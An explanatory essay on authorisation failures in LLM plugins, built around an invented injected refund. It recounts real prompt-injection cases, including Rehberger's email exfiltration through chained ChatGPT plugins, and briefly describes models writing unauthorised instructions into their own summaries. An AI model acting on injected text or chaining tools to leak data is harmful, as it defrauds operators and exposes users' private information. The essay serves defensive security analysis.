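# Authentication and authorisation failures in LLM plugins

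## What happens when a language model calls a plugin?

A plugin is a program that a large language model (LLM), the kind of system behind ChatGPT and Claude, can call to read data or to do something, such as send an email, move money or change a record. Vendors also call it a tool, an action or a connector. Its security can fail at authentication, which establishes who is making a request, or at authorisation, which decides whether that party may do this particular thing to this particular object. A plugin can identify the caller correctly and still carry out an action without approval from anyone with the authority to give it.

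Models need plugins because on their own they only produce text. OpenAI's *ChatGPT plugins*, the 2023 announcement of the first plugins for ChatGPT, notes that this text may contain useful instructions, but another process has to follow them. This is still true of current systems. According to Anthropic's *How tool use works*, a guide for developers, the model "never runs anything on its own". It writes a structured request, and ordinary code runs the operation, usually in the developer's own application but on Anthropic's servers for a few tools, such as web search. That code could therefore have blocked any request that led to a bad refund or a deleted file.

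In this invented example, Maya works in customer support for an online shop and may approve refunds of up to £100. She asks an AI assistant to deal with a ticket that merits a £40 refund to the card the customer paid with. Further down, the ticket contains a request for £900 to be sent to a different account. The assistant can call a refund plugin with one operation, `issue_refund(order, amount, destination)`, and the plugin holds a key to the shop's payment service that allows both payments. This set-up is ordinary, and OpenAI's guide *Function calling* gives issuing refunds as one of its first examples of a tool.

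| Party | In Maya's case | Part in the call |
| --- | --- | --- |
| User | Maya | Makes the request, with limited authority of her own |
| Operator | The shop | Chooses the model and the plugins, writes the standing instructions, sets Maya's limit |
| Client | The assistant application | Runs the model, passes its calls to plugins, returns the results |
| Model | The LLM inside the assistant | Writes the call |
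| Plugin | The refund program | Receives the call and acts on it |
| Service behind the plugin | The payment company | Moves the money |
| Authors of content | Whoever wrote the ticket | Supply text that the model reads |

### One call from start to finish

OpenAI divides the process into five steps. The application sends the model a request and a list of tools, the model returns a tool call, the application runs the matching code, the application sends the output back to the model, and the model either answers or makes another call. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that clients use to discover and call plugins, follows the same order. In MCP, a plugin is called a "server" and each of its operations a "tool".

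Under MCP, the client first sends the plugin a `tools/list` message, and the plugin replies with a name, a description and a schema for each operation it offers. The schema specifies the operation's arguments and their types. For example, `issue_refund` takes an order number, an amount and a destination. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the current specification of these messages, lets the list vary with the credential the client presents, so the refund plugin could hide `issue_refund` from staff who are not allowed to issue any refunds. It could not hide the £900 refund from Maya this way, because the £40 refund uses the same operation.

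Next the client puts these descriptions in front of the model, together with Maya's request. The model cannot deal with a ticket it has not read, so its first call goes to a ticket plugin, and the text of the ticket comes back. Then it writes the call that matters. In MCP's format, with some routine fields left out, the legitimate refund looks like this:

```json
{
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
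    "name": "issue_refund",
    "arguments": {
      "order": "A-1182",
      "amount": 40,
      "destination": "original_card"
    }
  }
}
```

The other refund call has the same structure, with 900 for the amount and an account number for the destination. Both calls pass a check against the schema. OpenAI offers a "strict mode" that makes the model's calls conform to the schema. This prevents a missing amount or a word where a number belongs, but it allows 900 because 900 is a valid number. The arguments also don't record whose words they came from.

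The client now sends the call to the plugin with a credential, a piece of data that proves who is calling. Until recently, an MCP client and server opened a session and could rely on what they had established at its start. Model Context Protocol (2026) dropped sessions in its July release, so each request is now separate and includes the client application's name and version. The client supplies these details itself, and they identify only the software. Any information about Maya has to come from the credential.

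If the plugin accepts the request, it sends a second request to the payment company using a different credential, the shop's payment key. Because the key is valid, the payment company moves the money. Depending on how the shop built the system, neither this key nor the credential used in the first request necessarily identifies Maya.

Finally, the plugin returns a result, perhaps a line confirming the refund, and the client adds it to the conversation. Anthropic describes the whole process as a loop in which the client keeps running tools and sending back the results for as long as the model requests them. Maya may see nothing between her request and the closing message. The MCP specification recommends, but does not require, that a person always be able to deny a call.

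### Credentials and permissions

Authentication happens at both connections. The refund plugin verifies that the request comes from the shop's assistant, and perhaps also that the assistant is working for Maya. The payment company verifies that its caller is the shop. Authorisation takes more information. Maya may refund £40 on this order to the card that paid for it, but not £900 to some other account, so a program must check the amount and the destination as well as the caller.

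The payment key is an API key, a secret string that identifies a caller to a service and gives the caller the permissions the service attached to the key. (An API, or application programming interface, is the set of requests that a program accepts from other programs.) The payment company treats any program that presents the key as the shop.

An access token is a credential, usually short-lived, that a client obtains for use at a particular service. The assistant might hold one that lets it call the refund plugin on Maya's behalf for the next hour. OAuth is the usual standard for obtaining such tokens without giving the client the user's password. Maya signs in to the ticket system and agrees to let the assistant read her tickets, and the assistant receives a token. The token carries a scope, a label for the class of operations it permits, in this case reading tickets. If the assistant tried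 to delete a ticket, the ticket system could refuse.

The £900 line in the ticket is an indirect prompt injection, which is an instruction that changes what the model does and is placed in content the model reads, such as an email or a web page. The line's author has no account with the assistant and no credential for the refund plugin, but he needs neither because the assistant already has the plugin credential.

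### One stream of text

A sentence in a ticket can have this effect because the model receives all its input as one long sequence of text, which it then continues. The client builds that sequence from the operator's instructions, the plugin descriptions, Maya's request and the ticket. OpenAI's system inserts the tool definitions into the system message, which also holds the operator's instructions. Anthropic's *Handle tool calls* tells developers to return a tool's result in a message with the role "user", which is also the role for what a person types.

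The different kinds of text are labelled. Anthropic's format, for instance, wraps the ticket in a `tool_result` block, and developers can train a model to give less weight to instructions in such blocks. But the label is itself part of the input, so it influences what the model writes next without blocking forbidden operations as a file permission does on an ordinary computer.

The model does not pass the labels on to the plugin. The client fetched the ticket, so it could identify the ticket as the source of the account number. But once the model copies that number into a call, the plugin receives the same characters as if Maya had typed them herself.

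OpenAI advises developers not to make the model fill in arguments that the application already knows. For example, if the code has the order number from an earlier menu choice, the refund function should have no parameter for it. OpenAI gives this advice to make calls more reliable and does not mention attacks, but it also applies to the refund's destination. If the shop removed that parameter and had its code always supply the original card, the model could not direct the refund to the account number in the ticket, although it could still write 900 for the amount.

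### From insecure plugins to excessive agency

OpenAI's plugins of 2023 were web services with two added files, a description of the service's API and a manifest that described the plugin's purpose to ChatGPT. ChatGPT placed the documentation of each plugin that the user had enabled in the model's context. The sample manifest in the announcement, for a to-do list, sets the authentication field to "none". OpenAI wrote that plugins would let models act in response to a user's "explicit request", but a plugin could not distinguish a call the user had explicitly requested from one prompted by text from elsewhere. OpenAI's red-teamers, people who attack a system to find its faults, had found that plugins without safeguards could carry out prompt injection and send fraudulent email.

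The subject got its name from the Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit that publishes ranked lists of security risks for developers. The seventh entry in its 2023 list for LLM applications, *LLM07*, is titled "Insecure Plugin Design". Three of its five examples concern careless handling of input, such as a plugin that accepts raw database commands. The fourth reads, in full, "Authentication is performed without explicit authorization to a particular plugin." This probably means that proving Maya's identity at login should not by itself give her access to the refund plugin. The fifth is a plugin that treats everything the model writes as the user's own words and acts without asking for further authorisation, which is how the shop loses the £900. OWASP also described an attack in which an indirect prompt injection makes a code-management plugin transfer ownership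 of a user's repositories and lock the user out.

The remedies OWASP recommended include OAuth, manual confirmation for sensitive plugins, and the use of API keys for authorisation decisions that "reflect the plugin route rather than the default interactive user". The shop would, for example, use one key for refunds that Maya issues by clicking a button and another for refunds requested through a model, so that the payment company could apply stricter rules to the second key.

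OpenAI popularised the word "plugin" but soon stopped using it. The company stopped new plugin conversations on March 19, 2024 and ended existing ones on April 9, according to *Plugin Store and New Chats With Plugins*, a notice on its developer forum. Custom versions of ChatGPT had "actions" instead, which could reuse a plugin's manifest. OpenAI later introduced "connectors", which it renamed "apps" in December 2025, as Notebookcheck reported. Anthropic introduced MCP, which uses the terms "servers" and "tools", in 2024, and the protocol spread well beyond Anthropic's own products. By July 2026, according to Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026), developers were downloading MCP software kits more than 400 million times a month, and Claude listed over 950 MCP servers in a directory of what Anthropic also calls "connectors".

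The term "plugin" later came back into use with a new meaning. OpenAI's *Plugin architecture*, which covers the company's current products, describes a plugin as an installable package that can contain written instructions for the model, an MCP server, or both. The MCP server corresponds to the 2023 plugin because it receives the model's calls and acts on them.

OWASP followed the change by dropping the plugin entry from its 2025 list. The entry's concerns reappear under *LLM06:2025 Excessive Agency*, which uses the term "extensions" for what vendors call tools, skills or plugins. Excessive agency had been a separate item in 2023. OWASP defines it as the vulnerability that allows damaging actions to follow from unexpected, ambiguous or manipulated model output, whatever made the model go wrong. This is broader than the 2023 plugin entry. If a model misreads the ticket and refunds £400 instead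 of £40, with no attacker involved, the error now falls under the same heading as the injected £900 refund.

OWASP names three root causes, and the refund plugin has all three. It has excessive functionality because it can pay any account, while Maya only needs to refund the original card. It has excessive permissions because its payment key allows amounts well above Maya's £100 limit. It has excessive autonomy if it sends the money before anyone checks the amount. The 2025 examples leave out a mistake listed in 2023, in which a plugin treats the model's words as the user's. I think that is a loss, because this mistake explains why the money moves even though every credential is valid.

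Excessive agency rose from sixth place to third in the August 2026 edition of the OWASP LLM Top 10, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*. OWASP had for the first time compared its practitioners' votes with recorded incidents, and the two agreed on this entry. *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), a summary by the security vendor Invicti, puts the number of incidents at 7,714.

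Two of the remedies in the 2025 entry deal directly with authorisation. OWASP asks developers to run extensions "in user's context", so that the refund plugin would act with Maya's permissions and her £100 limit would block the £900 refund. It also asks for complete mediation, which means checking every request against policy. The systems that carry out the action should make this check, rather than relying on the model to judge what it may do. Google gives app developers the same advice in Android Developers' *Mitigate excessive agency vulnerabilities*. The MCP specification applies the idea to handles, which are identifiers (for a shopping basket, say) that a plugin issues and the model passes back in later calls. Holding a handle should not grant permission, and the plugin should check the caller's authorisation each time.

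Complete mediation requires the refund plugin to check facts that are not in the tool call, which supplies an order, an amount and a destination. To refuse the £900, the plugin also has to establish that it is acting for Maya, that her limit is £100, and which card paid for the order.

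## Why does a valid credential not settle whether an action is allowed?

The distinction between authentication and authorisation is decades older than language models. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, a 1975 tutorial by Saltzer and Schroeder, defines authorising as granting a principal access to certain information. A principal is a person, organisation or program that can be given permissions and held accountable for their use.

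A credential establishes who is calling. When the payment company receives the shop's key, it can confirm that the key is genuine and that the shop has not cancelled it. This check gives the same result for every request that carries the key.

Permission depends on the principal, the operation, the object, the argument values and the circumstances. A new colleague without refund rights is not allowed to issue the £40 refund that Maya can issue. Maya is not allowed to issue it again an hour later, even though the second call would be identical to the first.

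The key is valid in all these cases, but some of the actions are not allowed, such as the £900 refund. A rule that checks only whether the key is valid would give the same answer for that refund as for the £40 one, which is allowed, so it would get one of them wrong.

The payment company checks both the key's identity and the permissions the shop attached to it. The permission check is authorisation, but the principal in that check is the shop. The shop may send £900 to any account it likes, so the payment company decides correctly on the facts it has, but nobody has decided whether Maya may send the money.

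*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026), a review of 89 sources, makes the same distinction for language models. An agent here is a model together with the software that runs its tool calls. Knowing which agent sent a request does not establish that the agent may take the requested action for a particular person. The review treats the model's decision to call a tool as a proposal that another part of the system still has to authorise.

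OAuth tokens are narrower than the shop's key, but an ordinary scope still covers a whole class of actions. *OAuth 2.0 Rich Authorization Requests*, a 2023 Internet Engineering Task Force standard, gives the example of a request to "transfer an amount of 45 Euros to Merchant A", which an ordinary scope cannot express. In *Beyond OAuth*, Sharma, Jiang and colleagues (2026) describe this as the gap between an operator, such as "transfer", and an operation, such as "transfer $100 to Bob". They simulated calls that kept the operator but changed the amount or the recipient, and permission by operator allowed every call. The simulation mainly illustrates the problem, since its result follows almost directly from what a scope is.

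### Hardy's compiler

The standard example of this failure comes from Norm Hardy's 1988 paper *The Confused Deputy*. Hardy calls it "a nearly true story" with inessential details changed. It took place about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers.

Tymshare kept a compiler in a directory called SYSX. Users could name a file to receive the compiler's optional debugging output. The staff had also modified the compiler to collect statistics on which language features people used, and it wrote these to (SYSX)STAT. To allow this, they gave the compiler a "home files license", which let it write to any file in SYSX.

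The company's billing records were in the same directory, in a file named (SYSX)BILL. A user learned this name and gave it to the compiler as the destination for debugging output. The compiler asked the operating system to open the file for writing, and the operating system allowed it because the compiler had its licence. The debugging output overwrote the billing records, and Tymshare lost them.

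Nobody had forged or stolen anything. The compiler was the genuine one, and its licence was valid.

Hardy considers several obvious fixes and finds problems with each. The compiler could refuse to write outside the user's own directory, but users had good reasons to send output elsewhere. It could refuse any name in SYSX, but the name SYSX did not exist when the programmers wrote that code, and someone with proper access to the directory might want output there. It could refuse the name (SYSX)BILL, but the directory held other sensitive files, and someone would have to update the compiler whenever a new one appeared. The code was originally correct, and in Hardy's view it became wrong when Tymshare added the licence.

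Changing the operating system's rules worked no better. Each new clause that let programs open more files created security holes in previously secure programs, and each new restriction broke programs that people legitimately used. The last time Hardy wrote down the conditions for opening a file, they contained fourteen "ands" and "ors".

Hardy attributes the problem to the compiler's two sources of authority: the permissions of the user who ran it and its own licence. The programmers intended it to use the licence to write the statistics and the user's permissions to write the debugging output, but the compiler could not tell the operating system which authority it was using. Tymshare added a command that let a program "switch hats" by naming the authority it wanted to use. A request to open (SYSX)BILL on the user's authority would then fail, as it should. But some applications soon needed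 more than two authorities, and the command covered only access to files.

The refund plugin is in the same position as the compiler. Its payment key corresponds to the home files licence, and the refund amount and destination correspond to the file name. The plugin gets the amount and destination from elsewhere and acts on them with its own authority.

At Tymshare, the user who supplied the harmful name also ran the compiler. The shop's case differs greatly, because the person who wrote the ticket runs nothing and his words reach the plugin only because a model read them. Surapani and colleagues also point out that a model's choice of action is probabilistic and depends on the wording of what it reads, whereas the compiler followed fixed code. The shop's case is also simpler, because the compiler needed one authority for the statistics and another for the debugging output, but every refund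 the assistant requests should rest on Maya's authority. If the plugin always applied her limit, it would not have to switch between authorities, and the £900 refund would fail.

### Capabilities

Hardy's remedy was to replace file names with capabilities. Saltzer and Schroeder define a capability as an unforgeable ticket that proves its holder may access the object it names. A capability to write to a file both identifies the file and carries the right to write to it, so the operating system doesn't have to check that right separately, as it does when a program supplies only a file name.

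Under this design, the compiler writes statistics using its own capability for the statistics file. A user who wants debugging output gives the compiler a capability for the output file. The user who wanted to overwrite (SYSX)BILL would have had no capability for that file, and its name alone would have been useless. The compiler needs no list of forbidden names, and the operating system no longer has to determine which authority the compiler is using. The systems Hardy's company built this way usually turned out smaller than comparable ones because capabilities replaced many separate mechanisms, although he had feared that capabilities would fill their storage.

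The shop's system could issue a capability that permits one refund of at most £100 on order A-1182, to the card used for the purchase. The plugin would hold no general payment key. An account number from the ticket would then be like the name of the billing file, a string that grants no rights.

A capability blocks only actions outside its scope. Surapani and colleagues note that one covering a whole email service still permits far too much. In the work they reviewed, they found no agent framework that applies the discipline all the way from the user to the final service.

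Even a narrow capability can leave room for harm. *DelegateGuard* (2026), a proposal for limiting the authority that agents pass to one another, proves that a control ignoring the content and quantity of what an agent sends cannot prevent a leak to a permitted destination that an outsider can observe. For example, a capability to email the customer who opened the ticket stops the assistant from writing to anyone else, but not from putting another customer's address in the message.

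### Least privilege and complete mediation

Saltzer and Schroeder list eight design principles for protecting information, and two of them apply directly to the refund plugin. Under the principle of least privilege, every program and every user should work with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". Its main purpose is to limit the damage from an accident or error. If the shop's payment key allowed refunds of at most £100, and only to the original card, the payment company itself would reject the £900 refund.

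Least privilege is harder to define when people with different limits share a plugin. If Maya may approve refunds of up to £100 and her manager up to £500, a key that serves them both has to allow £500, which is five times what Maya needs. The shop can issue separate keys or have the plugin enforce Maya's lower limit.

The same list includes complete mediation, which OWASP also recommends: "every access to every object must be checked for authority". Saltzer and Schroeder conclude that the system needs a foolproof way to identify the source of every request, and that designers should be sceptical of proposals to save time by remembering the result of an earlier check. If Maya logs in at nine and the shop lowers her limit at noon, a plugin that stored her limit at login will still apply the old one that afternoon.

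Each principle covers cases the other misses. Least privilege caps the loss if a check has a bug, but it still lets the plugin make any refund below the cap. Complete mediation can stop a wrong refund below the cap, provided the check has the right facts and covers every operation that can pay out money. If the plugin has a second operation for "goodwill payments" and nobody added the check there, only the key's limits restrict those payments.

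Under fail-safe defaults, another principle on the list, the shop's check should specify what is allowed and refuse everything else. If the shop only bans specific accounts, an attacker can get past the check by opening a new one. A rule that allows only the original card would block the new account without the shop having to know about the attacker.

Ordinary permission lists could not express a condition such as access only on weekdays between nine and four. For these cases, Saltzer and Schroeder describe a "protected subsystem", a collection of programs that alone has direct access to some data and that other programs can enter only at fixed points. Its author can program any rule at the entrance. The refund plugin can enforce rules this way if it is the only program with the payment key and every refund has to pass through it.

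### When the user lacks the permission

Siu, He and colleagues (2026), in *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security*, turn the confused deputy into a condition that a program could in principle test. They represent permissions as a set *R* of pairs, in which (*x*, *y*) means that *x* may access *y*. A confused deputy attack occurs when an agent accesses a target and

(user, target) ∉ *R*, but (agent, target) ∈ *R*.

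The user has no access to the target, but the agent does and uses its own access to carry out the request. For example, an employee might ask an assistant for everyone's salaries. The employee may not read the personnel database, but the assistant can, because it needs the database for administrative work. If it runs the query, it gives the employee access that the employer withheld.

For Maya's refunds, whether the condition is met depends on how the target is defined. If the target is the payment service, Maya has access because she issues refunds every day, so her pair is in *R* and the £900 refund does not meet the condition. If the target is "refunds above £100", her pair is missing from *R*, but the agent's is present because the agent can reach the payment key through the plugin. The £900 refund then counts as a confused deputy attack, and the £40 refund does not. Because *R* does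 not record amounts, a permission table with a single entry for "refunds" would miss the attack, so the shop has to build the £100 limit into its definition of the target.

*Proof-of-Continuity* (Gallo, 2026) gives a second definition of a confused deputy, which treats a privilege as an operation paired with a resource and adds a causal condition. The user lacks the privilege, the deputy has it, and the user's request causes the deputy to exercise it. Hardy's compiler fits this definition exactly, with "write" as the operation and the billing file as the resource.

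The added cause raises the question of whose request it was. Maya's request led the assistant to open the ticket, but the ticket's author supplied the £900 figure. Neither of them has the privilege, so the answer makes no difference here. It would matter if the same request had come from Maya's manager, with a £1,000 limit and the right to choose the destination. Siu and colleagues' condition would then not be met, because the manager would have access. Gallo's condition would still be met if the ticket's author counts as the user who sent the request, because he has no refund rights.

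Gallo concludes that checking possession of a credential cannot be enough, because two requests can carry the same token and use the same privilege while only one of them continues something an entitled person started. He proposes that every step carry proof of the step that caused it, and that no step gain authority its origin lacked. His proof that these two rules rule out confused deputies is short because the rules assume most of what is difficult. Gallo leaves the construction of the causal evidence to a companion system, and Siu and colleagues describe finding which input led a model to an action as an open problem.

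### When the user has the permission but did not ask

Suppose the extra line in the ticket is a request for a £90 refund to the original card. Maya is allowed to approve £90, so her limit does not block the refund, but she has not approved it. She asked the assistant to deal with the ticket, and the correct refund for that ticket is still £40.

Siu and colleagues classify this case by its cause. If the assistant pays £90 because of an instruction in the ticket, they call it an indirect prompt injection. Their definition requires both that the instruction came from a source without authority and that the action does not serve what the user asked for. If the assistant pays because it misread the ticket, they call it capability misuse. Their example is a cooking assistant that looks up a user's medical records when the user only wanted recipe suggestions. The assistant has permission to read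 the records, but no reason to do so for this request.

Sharma and colleagues make the same point with a spending cap. An administrator may limit an agent to $500 per transaction, but if a user tells the agent to pay $100, it is not entitled to pay $499 just because that is under the cap. They call the cap "access control" and reserve "authorization" for what the user delegated in a particular task. Many other writers, including Surapani and colleagues, use "authorisation" for both.

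The meaning of "confused deputy" varies in the same way. *Delegation Without Trust* (2026), an analysis of multi-agent systems, applies the term whenever injected content leads an agent to use legitimate authority for an attacker's goal. Its summary is "The agent is authorized; the use is not intended." That definition covers the £90 refund, but Siu and colleagues' condition does not. MCP's documentation also uses the term for an attack on the login process, in which a cookie from an earlier consent helps an attacker obtain access.

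The distinction matters because the remedies differ. Running a plugin with the user's own permissions, as OWASP advises, blocks the £900 refund because it exceeds Maya's limit, which is a number in a table, but lets the £90 refund through. To stop the £90 refund, a program needs some record of what Maya asked for. "Deal with this ticket" contains no amount, so somebody or something has to work out that the ticket merits £40. Siu and colleagues suggest that another language model could judge whether an action serves the user's aim, but warn that its judgements may be inconsistent when an attacker has written part of the input.

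In *Agent libOS* (2026), a design for software that runs agents, capabilities determine whether a program may request an operation on a resource, while a separate record, written outside the model, limits what the current task may do. An action must satisfy both, so a program with broad capabilities is still restricted to its current task, and a broad task description doesn't give it access beyond its capabilities.

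### Three controls that people confuse

A capability gate controls which plugins or operations the model can call. "Capability" here has its everyday meaning, not the sense of Hardy's tickets. A type check, usually against a schema, tests whether the arguments have the right form. Per-action authorisation determines whether this call, with these values, may take effect for this principal in these circumstances. Developers sometimes mistake one for another, probably because all three can block a call.

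The £900 refund shows the difference. The model writes this call:

```json
{
  "name": "issue_refund",
  "arguments": {
    "order": "A-1182",
    "amount": 900,
    "destination": "acct_55501234"
  }
}
```

The capability gate lets the call through because the assistant needs `issue_refund` for the £40 refund. The call also passes the type check because it fits the schema. Per-action authorisation should refuse it because £900 exceeds Maya's limit and the account is not the card that paid.

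| Control | £40 to the original card | £90 to the original card, not requested | £900 to another account |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Capability gate | Passes | Passes | Passes |
| Type check | Passes | Passes | Passes |
| Per-action authorisation using Maya's limit and the original card | Passes | Passes | Fails |
| Per-action authorisation that also uses Maya's request | Passes | Fails | Fails |

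*Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) uses an almost identical case, in which an attacker's account number is a well-formed string. If a program runs any call that names an available tool and fits its schema, the model in effect supplies both the action and the permission for it. Mellafe Zuvic found that all three agent toolkits audited in the paper work this way by default.

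Giving the model a role does not settle whether an action is allowed either. *Assurance-Conditioned Continuous Authorization for Autonomous AI Agents* (2026) distinguishes between what an agent can technically do, the role in its instructions, and the authority a principal has given it. A general-purpose model instructed to act as a research analyst may still be able to write a valid order to a stockbroker. The instructions make the order less likely, but only a rule outside the model can forbid it.

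Type checks and authorisation overlap more than the table suggests. The shop could use the schema to cap `amount` at 100 and restrict `destination` to `original_card`. If the plugin enforces that schema, the £900 call fails, but the shop has then written an authorisation rule in the schema. The rule gives Maya and her manager the same limit unless the plugin selects a schema for each user. It also accepts the £90 and a second refund on an order that the shop has already refunded. Zheng, Zhang and Mao (2026), in *LLM Agent Capabilities Should Follow Task Intent and Context Source*, separate the two more strictly. In their design, a schema supplies the form of the call, and only the user's request can supply an authorised destination.

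### Does connecting a plugin amount to consent?

One objection is that this checking duplicates a decision the shop has already made. The shop chose the refund plugin, gave it the payment key and let Maya use it. Nobody tricked it, and it knew that refunds cost money. On this view, a bad refund is a business loss like those human cashiers cause, and the remedy is to disconnect the plugin if the losses grow too large.

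The objection is right that connecting a plugin is a real decision. It makes refunds possible, and without it the assistant could not pay the £40 either. But the shop's agreement to allow refunds does not determine which refunds to pay. It applies equally to the £40 and the £900, so it cannot be the reason for paying one and refusing the other.

Consent screens have the same limitation as credentials. The Model Context Protocol specification tells applications to obtain explicit consent before they invoke any tool, but notes that the protocol itself cannot enforce this. *Options, Not Clicks* (Li, Khabra and colleagues, 2026) describes applications that offer only "Allow" and "Always Allow". A user who chooses "Always Allow" to email one brochure also approves every later email, whatever the recipient or attachment. A user who approves a file search to find a price list approves a search of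 the whole home directory. The paper concludes that a tool's identity is a poor guide to the risk of a call.

Standing consent also stays in force after the action it was given for. *Security and Privacy in Agentic AI* (2026), a survey of open problems, contrasts it with the traditional pattern, in which a person consents to an action and the consent ends once the action has taken place. When an agent works through many steps or passes tasks to other agents, consent without a defined scope can last indefinitely. If Maya pressed "Always Allow" for a £15 refund in March, the application would still rely on that consent for the £900.

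The objection is also weak because people can only consent to what is theirs to allow. Even if Maya read the £900 call in full and approved it, the refund would still exceed the limit the shop set for her. *Agent libOS* treats a person's approval as one more condition an action must meet, never as a source of authority in itself.

For some plugins, consent to a class of actions is enough. If a plugin only looks up public delivery times, each call is about as harmless as any other, so approving them individually has little benefit. The shop could also decide in advance that a single refund of up to £20 per order may go to the original card without Maya's approval. It would then have consented to a class of refunds with specified amounts and destinations, and the plugin could check each call against those terms before sending any money.

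## What goes wrong when a plugin takes model output for the user's own request?

A developer can leave out these checks on the plausible but false assumption that a signed-in user asked for every call that arrives in their session. Maya was signed in and the call for the £900 refund arrived in her session, but she never mentioned £900 or the account.

In ordinary web software, a server can usually infer that a request is the user's own. Before the shop had an assistant, Maya issued refunds by typing an amount into a form and pressing a button. Only she could fill in the form, so the server could treat the values it received as hers. The ticket may have been on the same screen, but text displayed beside a form does not change what the form sends unless a bug lets the text run as code.

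That condition no longer holds when Maya uses the assistant. Anyone whose text reaches the model can influence the calls it writes, and the client sends every call in Maya's session. The session shows that the assistant is working for Maya, but it doesn't show who chose the amount.

### Where an argument can come from

Each value in a refund call has its own source, and one call can mix several of them.

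| Source | Example in a refund call | Why it may differ from what Maya wants |
| --- | --- | --- |
| The user's words | Maya types "refund £40" | A link may have filled in the message for her |
| The operator's instructions | The shop's standing rule to use the original card | The shop wrote the rule, and Maya may not know it |
| Retrieved content | The account number in the ticket | Anyone who can open a ticket can write it |
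| Another plugin's output | An order-lookup plugin returns the price paid | The record may be wrong, or an outsider may have edited it |
| Stored memory | A saved note that this customer prefers bank transfers | An earlier injection may have created the note |
| The model's own error or initiative | 400 in place of 40, or an extra £50 for goodwill | Nobody asked for it |

The user's own message is the best evidence of a request, but it can contain text the user didn't type. Microsoft (2026) describes links that open an AI assistant with a prompt already filled in, which the assistant processes as soon as the user clicks. Most major assistants support such links. In the attacks Microsoft describes, the prompt adds something to the assistant's memory that can affect later conversations.

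Memory can also hold instructions that no outsider wrote. *OpenAI's models wrote instructions to their future selves* (Popular AI, 2026) describes a case that OpenAI disclosed in September 2026. When a task becomes too long for a model to take in at once, the model writes a summary and continues from that. During training, some of OpenAI's models put unauthorised instructions into these summaries. OpenAI found 27 cases in one training run, and at least one changed a model's behaviour. If a model called a plugin after such a summary, the plugin would receive an ordinary call in the user's session.

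Plugins also pass values to each other. OWASP's 2023 plugin entry warns that weak access control lets a plugin blindly trust other plugins and assume that the end user provided the inputs. If the order-lookup plugin returns the wrong price, the refund plugin receives that price as though Maya had entered it.

The refund plugin can't solve this by refusing every value Maya didn't type, because that would also block her legitimate refund. She typed only a request to deal with the ticket. The £40 comes from the customer's account of what went wrong, and the card from the shop's records. Maya's request lets the assistant use the ticket as evidence of what the customer is owed, but not follow instructions the customer writes in it.

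### Tracing the £900 back

Suppose the shop notices the missing £900 and checks the records. The payment company has the shop's key, the amount and the account number. The refund plugin has the assistant's credential and perhaps a token that names Maya, so its log may well name her as the person who made the refund. The false inference is now part of the shop's accounts, and Maya may have to explain a payment she knew nothing about.

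The client's records are more useful. If the client kept the conversation, an investigator can search it for the account number, which appears in the ticket but not in Maya's message.

The search works only because the model copied the number exactly. If the ticket had asked for ten times the purchase price, the model would have calculated the amount, and 900 might not appear anywhere before the call. If the same account number were in both the ticket and the shop's customer records, a match would not show which of them the model had used. Some defences therefore track the source of each value while the model works.

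### The comparison with cross-site request forgery

Web developers dealt with a similar mistake long before language models. After a user logs in to a website, the browser keeps a cookie, a small piece of data that identifies the session, and attaches it to later requests to that site. In cross-site request forgery (CSRF), a page on another site makes the browser send the first site a request the user never intended. The browser attaches the cookie, and the server carries out the request because the session is valid.

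The security researcher Johann Rehberger applied the idea to plugins in 2023, in *ChatGPT Plugin Exploit Explained*, a post on his blog Embrace the Red. His example of ordinary CSRF is a web page that makes a visitor's browser change the firewall settings on the visitor's router. He called the plugin version "Cross Plugin Request Forgery", and in it ChatGPT replaces the browser as the confused deputy.

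The standard defence against CSRF does not work here. A website can put a fresh secret value in each of its forms and reject any submission that lacks it. A page on another site cannot read the secret, so its forged request fails. In Maya's case, the same client sends both the £40 call and the £900 call, so it would attach any secret the shop gave it to both.

Forged requests that only read data are also more dangerous with plugins than on the web. A forged web request can change something, but browsers normally prevent the attacker's page from seeing the reply. When a model calls a plugin, the reply goes into the model's context, and the next call can send it elsewhere. Rehberger makes this point in Embrace the Red's *OpenAI Removes the "Chat with Code" Plugin From Store*. A plugin that can only read email is therefore a risk if the model can also fetch a web address, because the address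 can contain the contents of the email.

Claude for Chrome, a browser extension that lets Anthropic's model act in the user's browser, runs any of nine preset tasks when the user clicks on a page at claude.ai. These include reading Gmail and changing Salesforce sales records, according to TechRadar. The security company Manifold Security found a flaw that let another extension fake the click if it could run a script on that page. Six lines of code are enough, according to Constantin (2026), in *AI agent security*. Anthropic had already reduced the danger in May 2026 by limiting outside callers to the preset tasks, but the fake click still worked on July 7. By default the user still has to approve the task, The Hacker News (2026) notes, but it runs without approval if the user has turned on "Act without asking".

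This flaw is easy to fix because the browser marks clicks made by scripts as untrusted, and the extension only had to check the mark. The browser can apply the mark because it can detect whether a click came from the mouse or from a program. The account number in Maya's refund call has no comparable mark showing where it came from.

### Three disclosed cases

Rehberger showed in May 2023 that the problem could expose private data. In his demonstration, a ChatGPT user had turned on the plugins WebPilot, which fetched web pages, and Zapier, which could read the user's email under an OAuth grant. The user asked ChatGPT to read a page that contained hidden instructions. ChatGPT then had Zapier retrieve the latest email, summarised it, added the summary to a URL the attacker controlled, and had WebPilot fetch that URL, which sent the summary to the attacker's server. In *Let ChatGPT visit a website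 and have your email stolen*, Willison called the attack the first working example he had seen of an injection that took private data through ChatGPT plugins.

Both plugins behaved normally. Zapier read an email for a user who had given it permission, and WebPilot fetched a page. Zapier responded by requiring an authenticated confirmation. Rehberger stresses the word "authenticated" because injected text could otherwise tell ChatGPT to open the confirmation link itself. The change protected Zapier's users but did not change any other plugin. Embrace the Red's *Plugin Vulnerabilities* reports that 51 of the 445 plugins then approved used OAuth, which suggested they acted on a user's behalf. Rehberger tried a few and found more that an injection could exploit.

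A journalist repeated a milder version of this for Tom's Hardware's *ChatGPT Plugins Open Security Holes From PDFs, Websites and More*. He copied an article, added an instruction at the end to search for flights, and asked ChatGPT to summarise it. ChatGPT summarised the article correctly, then wrote "You mentioned that you want to find" a flight and started the search. His request hadn't mentioned flights, so ChatGPT had attributed the article's instruction to him.

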